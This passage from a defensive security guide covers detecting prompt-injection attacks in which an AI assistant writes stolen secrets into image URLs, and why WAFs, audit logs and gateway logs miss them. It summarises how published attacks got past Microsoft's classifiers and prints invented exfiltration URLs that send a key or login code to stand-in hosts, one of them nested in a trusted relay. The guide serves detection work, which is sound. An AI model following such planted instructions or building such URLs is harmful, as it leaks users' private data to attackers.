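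| Solo Enterprise for kgateway | None by default; otherwise the whole body, within a 1 MB buffer | None by default; otherwise the whole body, within a 1 MB buffer |

Most chat answers are short enough to fit within these response limits, so streaming is usually the bigger obstacle. To inspect a whole answer before the user receives any of it, the WAF has to hold the answer back until the model finishes. Solo's product works this way and does not support streaming. Akamai's *Optimize Text Streaming (Beta)* describes a delivery setting for AI applications that turns off response buffering to reduce delays.

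If the WAF lets the stream through as it arrives, the address comes in fragments. The invented address from earlier might arrive like this, with each piece in its own message:

`https://pic`

`tures.example/lo`

`go.png?ref=INV`

`ENTED-VALUE`

A rule that searches the raw stream for a complete address would fail, because other formatting separates the pieces of the address. The WAF would have to extract the text from each message, join the pieces and act before the last one reached the browser. Some products can inspect data as it flows. NetScaler's *Streaming support for request processing* describes a WAF that checks each field of an incoming form and forwards it while evaluating the next. A model's answer lacks the clear boundaries that separate form fields, so the WAF can't determine whether a half-written address will turn out to be harmless.

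Even a WAF that reassembled the answer perfectly could not reliably tell a stolen value from a normal one by searching for sensitive data. The employee asked for a summary of her own email, and the correct answer may well include an account number or a figure from the contract. Image links are also normal content. An unfamiliar host in an image address reveals the theft, and the application is better placed than the WAF to check for one before it displays the answer.

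### The image request

The image request goes straight to the attacker's server, so the WAF can't record or block it, even if the administrator has blocklisted the attacker's domain. If the assistant's own server makes the request, as in the provider-side attacks, the traffic leaves from behind the WAF, and the rules for incoming requests don't apply to it.

The relay attacks are a partial exception. In EchoLeak and SearchLeak, the browser's first request went to Teams and Bing respectively, both of which Microsoft runs. A WAF in front of Bing would have received the full address, including the nested address with the stolen data. But Bing's image search fetches pictures from addresses that users supply, so a rule against outside addresses would block the feature for everyone. A rule that also checked which page had triggered the request might be more selective, but Microsoft would have to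 write it, because its customers have no access to a WAF in front of Bing.

### What a WAF can catch

A WAF has the best chance of catching the attack when it starts with a link that opens an assistant with a prompt already filled in, as SearchLeak did. The instructions are in a parameter of the link, so they pass through the provider's WAF when the victim clicks it. ModSecurity rules can test a parameter by name, reject parameters that the developer didn't expect and measure the combined length of all parameters. In a normal search link, the parameter might contain a few words, so a web address or the notation for an image there deserves a closer look.

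A length limit alone would be less effective. An example rule in ModSecurity's manual flags requests whose parameters exceed 2,500 bytes, about 400 words of English, but an attacker could fit a complete set of instructions into much less. An attacker can also describe the address indirectly so that it doesn't appear in the link. A safer option than any of these rules is for the provider to put the text in the input box and wait for the user to press Enter.

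WAFs can also recognise known patterns in responses, within the limits above. A card number in a response may clearly indicate a leak on an ordinary web page, but it is weak evidence of one when the response comes from an assistant that reads private email. A log of such matches could still help after an incident by showing which answers contained the stolen item and when.

Repeated probing is easier to detect than a single attack. AWS's login protection counts failed logins from each network address and session, and a WAF can apply a similar limit to an assistant. Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian describe a shop's chatbot that gave customers' email addresses and delivery details to anyone who supplied an order number. Order numbers had a fixed prefix and six digits, so there were a million possible numbers, and the chatbot did not limit how many an outsider could try. Each question looked like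 normal customer service, but a long series of them from one visitor would look unusual.

Data theft through image requests can also take many attempts before it works. Cato's researchers had AI agents write and refine test cases for ReLeak, which probably produced far more prompts than an office worker would write. A provider that watches for this could notice an attacker who is still testing. But the attacker can test in their own account and then send the victim a single email, so the victim's employer would have no unusual series of requests to find.

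### Firewalls for AI applications

Several companies now sell filters that classify the text going to and from a language model. Cloudflare's version, formerly called Firewall for AI, became generally available in March 2026 as part of its web application firewall. It finds the prompt inside an incoming request and checks it for personal information, forbidden topics and attempts to override the model's instructions. Cloudflare's *AI Security for Apps* (2026), a product brief, describes a score, given to each prompt, that administrators can use in their own rules, for example to block a suspicious prompt only if it comes from a network address that has also been probing the login page.

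Unlike ordinary WAF rules, these classifiers can recognise a hostile instruction that contains no attack syntax, but they also make mistakes. If Cloudflare's filter doesn't recognise an application's format, it examines the whole request. Cloudflare acknowledges that a customer's name in an unrelated field can then trigger the check for personal information. Cloudflare's *AI Security for Apps*, a documentation page updated in August 2026, states that the filter handles only JSON requests. A document uploaded in another format would therefore reach the assistant unchecked.

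A filter's position, as well as its accuracy, affects what it catches. A filter in front of the application inspects the employee's request for a summary but not the stranger's email, which the application adds to the context afterwards. A filter between the application and the model can inspect both, because the application has assembled the full context by then. Zuplo's *Akamai AI Firewall* describes this arrangement, in which Zuplo's gateway sends the text to a classifier run by Akamai before calling the model, then sends the model's answer for a second check. If Akamai's service is unavailable, the gateway blocks the request by default, which takes the assistant offline too.

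Checking the answer raises the streaming problem again. In an earlier description of the integration, Zuplo's gateway collects five streamed messages before each check by default. Five messages may contain only a few words, so an image address could be split across several checks. The filter would have to keep the earlier text and hold back the new text until each check was complete. Otherwise the browser could request the image before the check finished, as it did in SearchLeak.

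Cloudflare's announcement gives neither a detection rate nor a false alarm rate. Cloudflare says its network handles about 20 percent of web traffic, which it hopes will help it spot new attacks early, but that figure doesn't measure how well the filter works.

Independent evidence about this kind of classifier comes mainly from EchoLeak and ReLeak, two attacks that used careful wording to get past Microsoft's protections. They don't show how often the classifier fails, and Microsoft's classifier is a different product from Cloudflare's and Akamai's.

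Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian also looked at Guardrails AI, a toolkit with ready-made checks for the input and output of language models. Most of the checks did not apply to the attacks in their study, but one that looks for dangerous SQL did. They compared the toolkit's features but did not test detection. A company considering any of these filters would learn more by using Lan and colleagues' method on its own assistant, with an invented secret and many wordings of the planted email.

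## What a security operations centre can and cannot see

A web application firewall inspects traffic at one point, but a security operations centre can combine records from many systems. However, none of the usual records contains everything an analyst needs to recognise the theft. The analyst needs the full address of the image request, because it contains the stolen data, and the model's answer, which would show that the assistant wrote that address. The analyst also needs a way to match the request to the answer, since an office browser loads images from many pages in the same minute.

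### What each record contains

The most useful record of an image request normally comes from the secure web gateway. Zscaler, which sells one, lists the fields its web log can contain, including the user's login name, the destination address, the content type, the request size and the referring page, which is the page that made the browser send the request. Each customer chooses which fields to send to its security information and event management (SIEM) system, the database in which a SOC searches its logs. A SOC may therefore lack the full address even though the gateway recorded it.

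When a page loads an image from another site, current browsers by default include the page's domain in the request but leave out the rest of its address. The log might therefore show that the request came from the assistant's site, but not which conversation triggered it.

A DNS log contains the host name that a device looked up, usually with the time and the device's network address, but never the URL's path or query string. If the attacker puts the stolen data in the host name, a DNS log is a good place to find it. DNS logs are a poor way to count requests because devices store the result of a lookup for a while and reuse it. The 40 image requests that CamoLeak needed to steal an access key all went to one GitHub host, so they might have caused only one lookup.

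Endpoint security software runs on the employee's machine, so it also works when she is at home. Lawrence (2025), in *Understanding SmartScreen and Network Protection*, describes two ways that Microsoft's version checks the reputation of websites. In Microsoft's Edge browser, the check uses the full address of each page but skips its images. In Chrome and Firefox on Windows, a separate component checks every connection, including those for images, but only by host name and network address. Neither check examines the full address of an image. Lawrence, who works on Microsoft Defender, writes that checking pages and downloads is enough for the phishing, malware and scam sites that the Edge feature targets, and that skipping the rest makes the feature faster.

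A company that builds its own assistant can log the model's answers. According to trackr.live's *Watch the Image Fetch*, a guide for security teams, most companies log neither what goes into their models nor what comes out. The guide cites no survey to support this, but its explanation is plausible, which is that some teams record only the details of each call to the model because answers can contain sensitive data. Even a complete log of answers would not show whether the browser loaded an image.

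| Record | Full image address | Model's answer | Link between them |
|---|---|---|---|
| Gateway log, traffic decrypted | Yes, unless the log drops part of it | No | User, time and often the assistant's site |
| Gateway log, traffic not decrypted | Host only | No | User and time |
| DNS log | Host only | No | Device and time |
| Defender's reputation check in Edge | No, it skips images | No | None |
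| Defender's reputation check in Chrome and Firefox | Host and network address | No | Device and time |
| Copilot audit record | No | No, only an identifier | User, time and conversation |
| Copilot messages stored in the user's mailbox | Possibly, as part of the answer | Yes | User and time |
| Log of a company's own assistant | Yes, if it includes answers | Yes, if it includes answers | Conversation, but not whether the image loaded |

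### Copilot's audit records

Suppose the employee with the full inbox uses Microsoft 365 Copilot, and the stranger's email makes Copilot write her colleague's access key into an image address. If her company has auditing turned on, Microsoft automatically creates a record of the conversation. The table shows the record's main fields for this case. Most of the fields come from Microsoft's list of common properties, and the network address and conversation identifier come from sample records in Microsoft's *Copilot interaction events overview*.

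| Field | Contents | In this case |
|---|---|---|
| `UserId`, `CreationTime` | The user and the time | The employee, at the time of her morning summary |
| `ClientIP` | The user's network address | Her laptop's address, or one that the whole office shares |
| `ThreadId` | An identifier for the conversation | Groups her questions and Copilot's answers |
| `AccessedResources` | The items Copilot opened, including emails and files | Should list the stranger's email and the colleague's |
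| `XPIADetected` | Whether Microsoft detected planted instructions in an item | Probably false, if the attack worked |
| `Messages` | An identifier for each prompt and answer | Shows that Copilot answered, without the text |
| `AISystemPlugin` | The extensions Copilot used, such as Bing web search | Nothing about images that her browser loaded |

No field on the list contains the answer or an image address, so an analyst with only this record could not tell the theft from a normal morning summary.

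The list of accessed items is still useful once the company knows which email carried the instructions, because an analyst can search every employee's records for that email's identifier and find out whose assistant read it. In EchoLeak, the planted text told Copilot not to cite the email, but the audit field is supposed to list everything Copilot accessed, cited or not. Microsoft's overview of these records mentions only files and documents when defining the field, so a company should first test whether emails appear there too.

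The flag for planted instructions depends on the same kind of protection that EchoLeak and ReLeak got past, so Microsoft may have missed the instructions if the flag is false. When the flag is true, a SOC has a good lead, because the record identifies the item that triggered it. The web search entry shows that Copilot consulted the public web through Bing. In SearchLeak, the employee's browser contacted Bing to load an image, so data can go through Bing even when the record contains no web search.

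Microsoft's pages differ on whether the audit log contains the conversation. The training material says the message field shows "prompts and responses", but the published sample records contain only identifiers in that field, and Robbins (2026), in *Collecting Microsoft 365 Copilot Data with Microsoft Purview eDiscovery*, states that audit logs omit the text. Microsoft keeps the text of prompts and responses in a hidden folder in the user's mailbox. An investigator can retrieve it with eDiscovery, a search tool that companies mainly use for legal and compliance cases. A separate Microsoft data security tool can also display it.

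If the company learns the attacker's domain, an investigator could search those mailbox folders for it. A keyword search returns only the messages that contain the word, but an optional setting adds the rest of the conversation from the 12 hours before and after. Robbins doesn't specify whether the stored answer keeps an image address exactly as the model wrote it. It might not, because in SearchLeak the browser acted on an early version of the answer that differed from the finished one. A company can test this by having Copilot write the address of a harmless picture on a server the company owns, then searching the mailbox for that address.

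To connect the conversation to an image request, the analyst has to compare the audit record with the gateway log. Microsoft notes that Copilot's audit details do not identify the user's device, so the analyst has to match the two by user name, time and a network address that a whole office may share. Suppose the audit record shows an answer at 9:14 and the gateway log shows the employee's browser contacting an unfamiliar host in the same minute. The timing suggests that the answer triggered the request, but a news site open in another tab could also have done so.

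Microsoft also keeps audit records for only 180 days by default, so a company that began searching its records on 3 December 2026, the day Cato published ReLeak, could go back only to 6 June. For AI applications from other companies, Microsoft creates audit records only if the customer turns on pay-as-you-go billing, so a company whose staff use both Copilot and a rival chatbot may have records only for Copilot.

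### Encrypted traffic and shortened addresses

Nearly all web traffic is encrypted, so a gateway has to decrypt it to read more than the host name. A user of Squid, a free web proxy, asked its mailing list why his log contained only host names although he had configured Squid to log full addresses. Li (2020) replied in *Is strip_query_terms supported in v4?* that without decryption Squid "has no idea what the browser is doing".

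The setting the user had changed matters once a company does decrypt its traffic. By default, Squid removes the query from each address before logging it, to protect users' privacy and keep the logs small. Take the invented image request from earlier, as the browser sends it:

`https://pictures.example/logo.png?ref=INVENTED-VALUE`

With decryption and Squid's default setting, the log contains:

`https://pictures.example/logo.png`

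Without decryption, it contains:

`CONNECT pictures.example:443`

Removing the query from logged URLs hides the most evidence in relay attacks. An attacker who sends data directly can put it in the path, which Squid logs. In a relay attack, the attacker's address is usually nested in the query, so the log omits both the attacker's host and the data. For SearchLeak, Squid's default log would have shown only a visit to Bing's image search.

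trackr.live's *The Model Writes the URL That Leaks Your Data* points out that if a company keeps full addresses, its gateway and SIEM will hold the same one-time codes and email titles that the attacker wanted. It recommends limiting who can read these logs and how long the company keeps them, and storing redacted extracts where possible. Without these precautions, the logs could lead to another leak.

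Many companies decrypt general web traffic but exempt Microsoft 365, and Microsoft encourages them to. One of its principles for connecting to the service is to bypass proxies and inspection devices, and it strongly recommends using its built-in security features instead of a second layer of network processing. One practical reason is that Copilot needs a connection that stays open during a chat. Microsoft warns that inspection can break this connection and leave Copilot "essentially nonfunctional". Cisco, whose products can decrypt this traffic, lists slow Outlook delivery and poor Teams performance among the symptoms of decrypting it. As an interim workaround, the company tells affected customers to exempt Microsoft's main service domains from decryption by Cisco's intrusion prevention system.

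During an attack like EchoLeak, a company that had followed this advice would have logged a connection to Teams but not the address that contained the stolen data. Zscaler labels such traffic "Not inspected because of O365 bypass" in its log, so a SOC can at least measure how much traffic it exempts. The exemption may also cover Bing, the relay in SearchLeak, depending on how the company wrote its list.

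Provider-side requests, such as those in ReLeak's file and sandbox attacks, leave nothing in the customer's gateway, DNS or endpoint logs, so better settings would not help.

### Small secrets and volume alerts

SOCs often look for data theft by volume, with an alert when a computer sends an unusual amount of data to an unfamiliar destination. This works against someone copying a customer database. A 40-character access key takes up 54 characters in an image address. If the alert triggers at 10 megabytes per user per day, the attacker could steal this many keys from one employee before reaching it:

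10,000,000 ÷ 54 ≈ 185,000 keys

Lowering the threshold to 10 kilobytes would still leave room for 185 keys, and it would flag a large share of ordinary browsing. A request's headers, which carry details such as the browser version and cookies, can easily be longer than the key, so loading a news site with a few dozen pictures would exceed the lower threshold. The 10,000-byte contract from earlier would also exceed it, because encoding expands the contract to about 13,300 characters.

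*How to Detect AI-Mediated Data Exfiltration in the Cloud* (Ben Naim, 2026) describes an invented case in which a support agent emails out a 28-kilobyte summary of 2,400 customer records. The destination is on the allowlist and the size is below the DLP threshold, so neither control raises an alert. Ben Naim proposes comparing each agent with its own past behaviour. The agent in his example normally sends emails of 200 to 800 bytes, so the stolen summary is 35 times its usual maximum. Ben Naim works for ARMO, which sells this kind of monitoring, and the example suits the company's product well. Comparing sizes would miss an agent that leaked a single 54-character key, because the email could stay within the normal range. His other signals, such as an agent reading a table it has never used before, might still help.

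Adding up small requests over a conversation can reveal a document sent in pieces, but trackr.live warns that a picture gallery or a dashboard that keeps reloading a chart would look much the same. The method does not help detect the theft of a single key, which needs only one request.

### The base rate

A SOC could instead inspect every image request with a more precise rule. Even a very accurate rule produces mostly false alerts when thefts are rare. Suppose a company has 10,000 employees whose browsers each load 2,000 images a day, which makes 20 million requests. Five of them carry stolen data. The rule catches all five and wrongly flags one in every 100,000 harmless requests:

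False alerts = (20,000,000 − 5) ÷ 100,000 ≈ 200

The share of alerts that are real is called precision:

Precision = real alerts ÷ (real alerts + false alerts)

Precision = 5 ÷ (5 + 200) ≈ 2.4%

In general, if a company makes N requests, M of them malicious, and the rule catches a share d of the malicious ones and wrongly flags a share f of the rest:

Precision = dM ÷ (dM + f(N − M))

The rule wrongly flags only one in 100,000 harmless requests, yet more than 97 percent of its alerts are false. Reviewing the 205 daily alerts at ten minutes each would take about 34 hours, more than four analysts could work in eight-hour shifts. For half the alerts to be real, the rule could wrongly flag only one in 4 million harmless requests.

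Five thefts a day is also a pessimistic assumption. A company that suffered five a year would receive about 73,000 false alerts over the same period, or one real alert for every 14,600 false ones. An analyst might work there for months without seeing a real alert, and would have good reason to expect the next one to be false.

The formula also suggests a way out, which is to inspect fewer harmless requests. Suppose the SOC can use the referring page to select image requests that came from AI assistants, and these make up 1 percent of the total. With the same false alarm rate, the arithmetic becomes:

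False alerts = 200,000 ÷ 100,000 = 2

Precision = 5 ÷ (5 + 2) ≈ 71%

The real figure would probably be lower. Assistants display charts and signed storage links, so the rule might make more mistakes on their traffic than on ordinary web traffic. The selection would also miss any image that loads somewhere else, as in the Copilot Cowork case, where the data left when the user opened a message in her inbox. But the example shows why the link between an answer and a request is worth recording, since the SOC would otherwise have to search all 20 million.

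### Excluding trusted hosts

According to trackr.live, analysts will mute a rule within a week if it flags every signed storage link. For a SOC that receives 200 false alerts a day, the obvious quick way to reduce them is to exclude hosts it trusts. Most of the alerts may come from a few busy services, so a short list of exclusions could remove nearly all of them.

This list has the same weakness as a browser's allowlist. trackr.live gives a sample search that finds long encoded values in gateway logs and then discards any request to an approved host. It warns that discarding those requests would hide EchoLeak and SearchLeak, which sent theirs to Teams and Bing. By the same reasoning, excluding `docs.google.com` would have hidden the Superhuman attack, and excluding `camo.githubusercontent.com` would have hidden CamoLeak.

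An exclusion can also outlast the reason for it. If an analyst excludes Bing from a detection rule because its image search triggers too many alerts, a colleague who joins a year later may not know. The SOC would then report that it monitors image requests for stolen data, and nobody would notice that the rule leaves out the relays most useful to attackers.

### SOC 2 audits

Companies that sell AI products often give customers a SOC 2 report as evidence of good security. Here, SOC stands for System and Organization Controls, not security operations centre. An independent accounting firm follows a standard set by the American Institute of Certified Public Accountants to examine a service provider's controls, which are the procedures and technical measures that protect customers' data. A Type 1 report covers the design of those controls on a particular date, while a Type 2 report also covers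 whether they worked over a period of months.

The auditor tests the provider's controls but does not search traffic for thefts. For an AI assistant, the auditor could test whether staff reviewed the image allowlist as often as the provider's policy requires, and whether a security engineer approved each new feature that displays the model's output. The auditor could also test the stored logs. If the policy requires the provider to keep full addresses for a year but its proxy removes the query from each one, this test should reveal the problem.

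Auditors usually test samples. If a provider made 250 changes to its assistant in a year and one of them skipped the security review, an auditor who picked 25 at random would have a 10 percent chance of including it. Sampling is a reasonable way to learn whether the provider normally follows its procedures, but the provider could release an unsafe renderer by missing just one review.

A provider can also follow its procedures and still have the flaw. An auditor might confirm that someone reviewed the allowlist every quarter, even though each reviewer left Bing on it because Microsoft owned the domain. To find the relay, a penetration tester has to test what the service does with a nested address. Customers should also check which products the report covers, because the provider chooses them and an assistant launched after the audit period won't be included.

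### How to read "no exploitation observed"

Announcements of these flaws often state that nobody has seen a real attack. AIAIAI.FYI's *Cato AI Labs details three ReLeak zero-click attacks on Microsoft 365 Copilot* (2026), for example, reports that Cato knows of no exploitation of ReLeak. This is reassuring only to the extent that Cato was likely to notice an attack.

Call the probability that someone exploited the flaw p, before hearing the statement, and the probability that the speaker would have detected it d. If the speaker reports nothing, the probability of an undetected attack is:

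p(1 − d) ÷ (p(1 − d) + 1 − p)

Suppose there is a 10 percent probability that an attack occurred, and a security team reports seeing none. If the team had a 5 percent chance of detecting an attack, its report lowers the probability only to 9.5 percent. If it had a 90 percent chance, the probability falls to 1.1 percent. These inputs are invented, but the same report can deserve very different amounts of trust depending on how likely the team was to detect an attack.

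Cato is probably near the low end. It sells gateways, so it may have been able to find some of its own customers' browser requests to Bing, but it could not search Microsoft's records.

Customers are in a similar position, except that they can look for any documents that ReLeak's file attack left in their storage. Copilot's audit records can list the files Copilot created as well as those it read, so a company could find documents it created before the fix on 11 November and check where their links lead. This search is more informative than most because an attacker might have had no way to delete such a document. A customer's report of seeing nothing adds almost no information about the sandbox attack.

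Microsoft could have learned the most, because it could in principle compare Copilot's answers with the addresses Bing's image search fetched, which customers can't do. But Bing routinely fetches images from outside addresses for legitimate reasons, so Microsoft also faces the base rate problem, and old records may have expired before Microsoft could search them.

A label such as "not exploited" leaves all of this out. A customer deciding whether to cancel keys or notify people whose data was at risk should ask Microsoft which records it searched, how far back they went and whether the search would have found the researchers' test attacks. The last answer is the easiest to check, because the researchers know when they ran their tests.

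## Detecting the leak in network traffic

If a company's gateway decrypts traffic and logs full URLs, the SOC can pick out the image requests that came from an AI assistant and run several detection rules on those, instead of searching all 20 million daily image requests for stolen data. Each rule misses some of the published attacks, and almost none of the rules help with requests from an AI provider's own servers.

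### Selecting the assistant's requests

The first step is to filter requests by the page or program that made them. For an assistant in a browser, the SOC keeps the requests whose referring page belongs to the assistant's site. For tools on the company's own servers, trackr.live suggests filtering by the account, container or network address range that the tools use. A company with both kinds of assistant needs both filters. SearchLeak's first request came from the victim's browser, so a rule limited to servers would have missed it.

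Suppose the selection leaves 100,000 requests a day, including the five thefts from the earlier example. With the same false alarm rate of one in 100,000:

False alerts = 100,000 ÷ 100,000 = 1

Precision = 5 ÷ (5 + 1) ≈ 83%

The same rule had a precision of 2.4 percent on all 20 million requests. If the company had five thefts a year instead of five a day, precision would fall to about 1.4 percent, with 365 false alerts for five real ones. An analyst could still handle that workload, because checking one alert a day takes ten minutes.

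Selecting requests by their referring page misses images that load outside the assistant's page. It also misses requests that don't include a referring page, which a site can tell browsers to leave out. Later rules never examine the missed requests, so a company should have each assistant display a harmless test image and check that the request for it is selected.

### Unfamiliar destinations

The next rule checks the host name in each selected request against a list of hosts the assistant normally contacts. If the host is not on the list, the SOC gets an alert with the host, the user and the time.

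trackr.live expects this list to be short, because an internal assistant tends to load most of its images from a few places, such as the company's document store and a chart service. For an assistant with a few hundred users, trackr.live estimates that checking the model's answers against such a list would turn up a handful of new hosts a day in the first week and almost none later. These figures are a practitioner's judgement, not measurements.

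A variant of the rule alerts on hosts that are new to the company. *GenAI Process Connection to Unusual Domain* (2025), a production rule from the security monitoring vendor Elastic, covers AI programs on Macs, including Claude, Cursor and Windsurf. It alerts when one of them contacts a domain that none of them has contacted in the previous seven days. Software on the Mac supplies the domain name, so the rule works without decrypting traffic. It could catch a leak like the one through Cursor's diagrams, where the editor contacted the attacker's server directly.

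The rule excludes more than 100 domains and patterns, including every host under `microsoft.com`, `google.com` and `githubusercontent.com`. These exclusions cover the first hosts in EchoLeak, the Superhuman attack and CamoLeak. The rule also excludes `amazonaws.com`, where any Amazon customer can rent a server, and it does not cover ordinary browsers. Once a domain has triggered an alert, it no longer counts as new, so a second victim in the same week would not trigger another alert.

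Elastic labels the rule's noise "Medium". It warns that vendors move to new domains and that developers trying out new AI tools will set off alerts.

### Decoding parameters and nested addresses

A host list can't reveal an attacker's address inside a request to a trusted service. For that, the SOC needs the full address and a program that takes it apart:

1. Split the address into its host, path and parameters.
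2. Decode percent codes in each part, such as `%2F`, which stands for a slash.
3. Try other common encodings, such as Base64url and hexadecimal, and keep any result that is readable.
4. If a result is itself a web address, return to step 1 with that address.
5. Stop after a fixed number of rounds.

Take the earlier relay example as it might appear in a log:

`https://preview.trusted.example/fetch?url=https%3A%2F%2Fcollector.example%2FINVENTED-VALUE`

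The first round finds the trusted host and one parameter, which decodes to a second address. The second round finds `collector.example` and the stolen value in that address. The rule alerts because `collector.example` is not on the list, even though the trusted host is.

The program may have to decode an address more than once. The percent sign has its own code, `%25`, so an address encoded twice contains `%252F` where the slash should be. The program also has to examine the path. According to trackr.live, the chart service QuickChart receives its diagrams in a query parameter, while Mermaid.ink receives them in the path. The encoded addresses in Camo links are in the path too.

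In the Superhuman attack, the decoder would have found no nested address because the data went to a form on Google's host. It would still have produced the text of the stolen emails, which the next rule could search.

### Searching the decoded values

DLP patterns work much better after decoding, so the rule searches each decoded value for sensitive data, such as card numbers, login codes or the company's own key formats, and reports what it found and where.

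In SearchLeak, the stolen email title was readable text with underscores in place of spaces. A rule that searches for the word "code" near a six-digit number would match such a title if it treated underscores as spaces.

The rule should search the values of parameters, not their names. The word filter that Lan and colleagues tested blocked any address containing words such as "token", "auth" or "credential". Amazon's signed storage links have a parameter called `X-Amz-Credential`, so such a filter would block harmless pictures if it ignored capitalisation. It could also miss a stolen key, which need not contain any of the listed words.

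Pattern matching also fails when the secret has no recognisable form. A price from a contract looks like any other number, and a four-character piece of a key could be almost anything.

### Why randomness is only a supplement

Security products often score how random a value looks by its Shannon entropy, calculated from the share p of the value that each character makes up:

H = −Σ p × log₂ p

The filter in Lan and colleagues' test blocked parameter values longer than ten characters if they scored above 4.0 bits per character. Typical access keys score 4.5 to 5.5, according to the paper. But the score depends on the length of the value and on how many different characters it uses:

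16 characters, all different: log₂ 16 = 4.0

Hexadecimal text of any length: at most log₂ 16 = 4.0

`Your_login_code_is_482913`: 4.05

A secret of 16 characters or fewer can therefore never exceed the threshold, however random it is, and a longer secret in hexadecimal can't either. The invented email title is mostly plain English but still exceeds the threshold, and many harmless chart labels of that length would too. Raising the threshold would let the title through, but the random-looking tokens in some signed links would still trigger the filter.

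trackr.live therefore recommends adding randomness to an alert's score without letting it decide whether to alert. If two requests go to unfamiliar hosts, for example, an analyst might start with the one that contains a long random value.

### A separate rule for each relay

The nested-address rule would flag almost every use of Bing image search, but a SOC that exempts Bing to stop these alerts will miss the next attack like SearchLeak.

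A rule for Bing alone can be much narrower, alerting when Copilot's page sends Bing image search an address outside Microsoft. An employee's own image search normally starts on a Bing page, so it would not trigger the rule. A rule for `docs.google.com` could alert when an assistant's page loads a form submission as an image. Camo handles outside addresses by design, so the number of images in one answer is a better signal there.

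To write such rules, the SOC needs other details about each service besides its host name. trackr.live suggests recording the service's permitted path and function, who owns the account or storage space, and whether the service may receive nested addresses. Approving a chart service also means sending it the company's data, which requires a separate decision.

These rules protect only against relays that someone has identified. Varonis recommends reviewing every approved domain for services that fetch addresses supplied by users, but Microsoft missed such a service in Bing, which it owned. A safer default is to alert on any outside address nested in an assistant's request until someone has examined the service receiving the request.

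### Repeated requests

Some thefts can be detected only by examining several requests together. The SOC can group requests by user, conversation and destination, then alert when a group contains too many requests or too much data. Gateway logs rarely identify the conversation, so the SOC may have to treat all requests from one user's assistant page within, say, ten minutes as a single conversation.

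CamoLeak needed 40 requests to send a 40-character key. An alert set at 20 images per host would have triggered after half the key had been sent. Measuring the total amount of data in the image addresses would have helped less, because CamoLeak encoded the key in the order of the requests. If an attacker instead splits a key into readable pieces, the SOC can join the values from a group of requests and run the DLP search again on the result.

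The best available test of this idea used model answers instead of network traffic. Chauhan and Revankar (2026), in *Caught in the Act(ivation)*, built 50 artificial conversations of 20 turns each, with the model leaking small pieces of a credential in four to eight turns. Checking each answer separately for planted values caught 6 percent of the conversations, while a running leakage score caught 90 percent, typically around the ninth turn, with no false blocks.

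That score came from a trained model that compared each answer with the real secret, so a simple counter at a gateway would probably do worse. The missed conversations leaked early and ended before the score reached the limit. An attacker could also start a new conversation to reset the score.

trackr.live doubts that most internal tools face an attacker patient enough to justify the false alarms that grouping causes on picture galleries and similar pages. That seems right for slow leaks over several days, but CamoLeak sent all its requests from one answer, and a count per answer costs little.

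### Canary tokens

A canary token is a marker value that nobody has a reason to use, such as a fake access key planted in an email. The SOC searches the decoded values for the exact marker. A match proves that data from that email has left the network, which pattern matching and randomness scores cannot prove.

The search has to run after decoding, because a plain text search misses an encoded marker. Base64 encodes bytes in groups of three, so the same marker can appear in three different forms depending on where it starts within a group.

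Chauhan and Revankar give a simple formula for the chance of catching a thief who takes one key at random. If the context contains m real keys and k fake ones, and the search misses a share β of leaked fakes:

Probability of detection = k ÷ (m + k) × (1 − β)

With one real key, three fakes and a miss rate of 1 percent:

3 ÷ 4 × 0.99 ≈ 74%

Nine fakes would raise this to 89 percent. An attacker who takes every key would also take the fakes, so one fake could be enough. But the formula fails if nearby text shows which key is real. Fake keys also don't help against an attacker who wants something else, such as an email title.

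In the main test, searching the model's answers for planted values caught 30 percent of attacks and raised no false alarms on harmless prompts. Adding a filter on incoming text raised detection to 82 percent but also raised the false alarm rate to 15 percent. In a separate small test, the search caught 99 percent of the cases where a planted fake key leaked. The low rate in the main test is therefore a reason not to rely on the stolen data containing a planted value.

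*Enhancing Security in LLM Applications* (2025) tested two security tools, Vigil and Rebuff, that put a marker word beside the developer's instructions and search the model's answers for it. In their default form, the tools detected none of the study's attempts to extract those instructions. A marker works only if the model copies it into its answer, so it should be part of something an attacker would want rather than a label next to it.

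A match proves a leak but not an attack, so the analyst still has to find out why the marker left. An employee might have forwarded the email, or the chat site might have sent the marker to an advertising tracker. *Penny for Your Prompts* found that several chat sites sent users' prompts to such trackers.

A fake login can provide a second alert if the company monitors the system that the login appears to open. When the thief tries the login, the company learns of the theft, even if the data left from the provider's servers. Such an alert could have exposed an attack like ReLeak's sandbox route, but only if the attacker stole the fake login and used it.

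### Six requests through the rules

Suppose the company's assistant runs at `assistant.example`. Its approved hosts are `files.example`, `charts.example` and the link-preview service `preview.trusted.example`. The company has planted a fake key, `DECOY-7Q4M`, in the employee's inbox. Within one minute, the gateway decrypts and logs these invented requests from her browser:

| Request | Referring page | Address |
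|---|---|---|
| 1 | `news.example` | `https://ads.example/pixel.gif?id=RANDOM-VALUE` |
| 2 | `assistant.example` | `https://files.example/photo.png?signature=RANDOM-VALUE` |
| 3 | `assistant.example` | `https://charts.example/bar?labels=Code_A,Code_B&values=482913,377120` |
| 4 | `assistant.example` | `https://pictures.example/logo.png?ref=INVENTED-VALUE` |
| 5 | `assistant.example` | `https://preview.trusted.example/fetch?url=https%3A%2F%2Fcollector.example%2FYour_login_code_is_482913` |
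| 6 | `assistant.example` | `https://charts.example/bar?labels=DECOY-7Q4M&values=1` |

The random values stand for long strings, and the one in request 4 is the colleague's encoded key. The rules give these results:

| Request | Alert? | Reason |
|---|---|---|
| 1 | No | It came from a news site, so the selection drops it |
| 2 | No | The host is approved and the value matches no sensitive pattern |
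| 3 | Yes, a false alarm | The DLP rule finds "code" near a six-digit number, but these are sales figures for two product codes |
| 4 | Yes | The host is unfamiliar |
| 5 | Yes | The nested host is unfamiliar, and the decoded text contains a login code |
| 6 | Yes | The address contains the fake key |

No host received enough requests to trigger a limit on repeats. The analyst should start with request 5, because the login code may work for only a few more minutes. Request 6 needs more investigation. It sent the fake key to an approved chart company, perhaps because the employee asked for a chart of her email or because an attacker can read that company's records.

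A simpler rule that matched long random values in requests to unapproved hosts would have flagged requests 1 and 4. It would have raised a false alarm on an advertisement and missed the login code and the fake key.

### Rules published after SearchLeak

Microsoft had already fixed SearchLeak on its servers when Varonis published the attack, so detection advice was mainly useful for searching old logs and catching similar attacks. Varonis told security teams to look for Copilot Search links whose `q` query parameter contained HTML or instructions to put data in image addresses. Two days later, ThaiCERT's *Microsoft 365 Copilot Vulnerability Could Allow Data Theft Through a Link Click* (2026), an official notice from Thailand's national computer emergency team, gave similar advice and also told administrators to review abnormal connections to Bing's image services.

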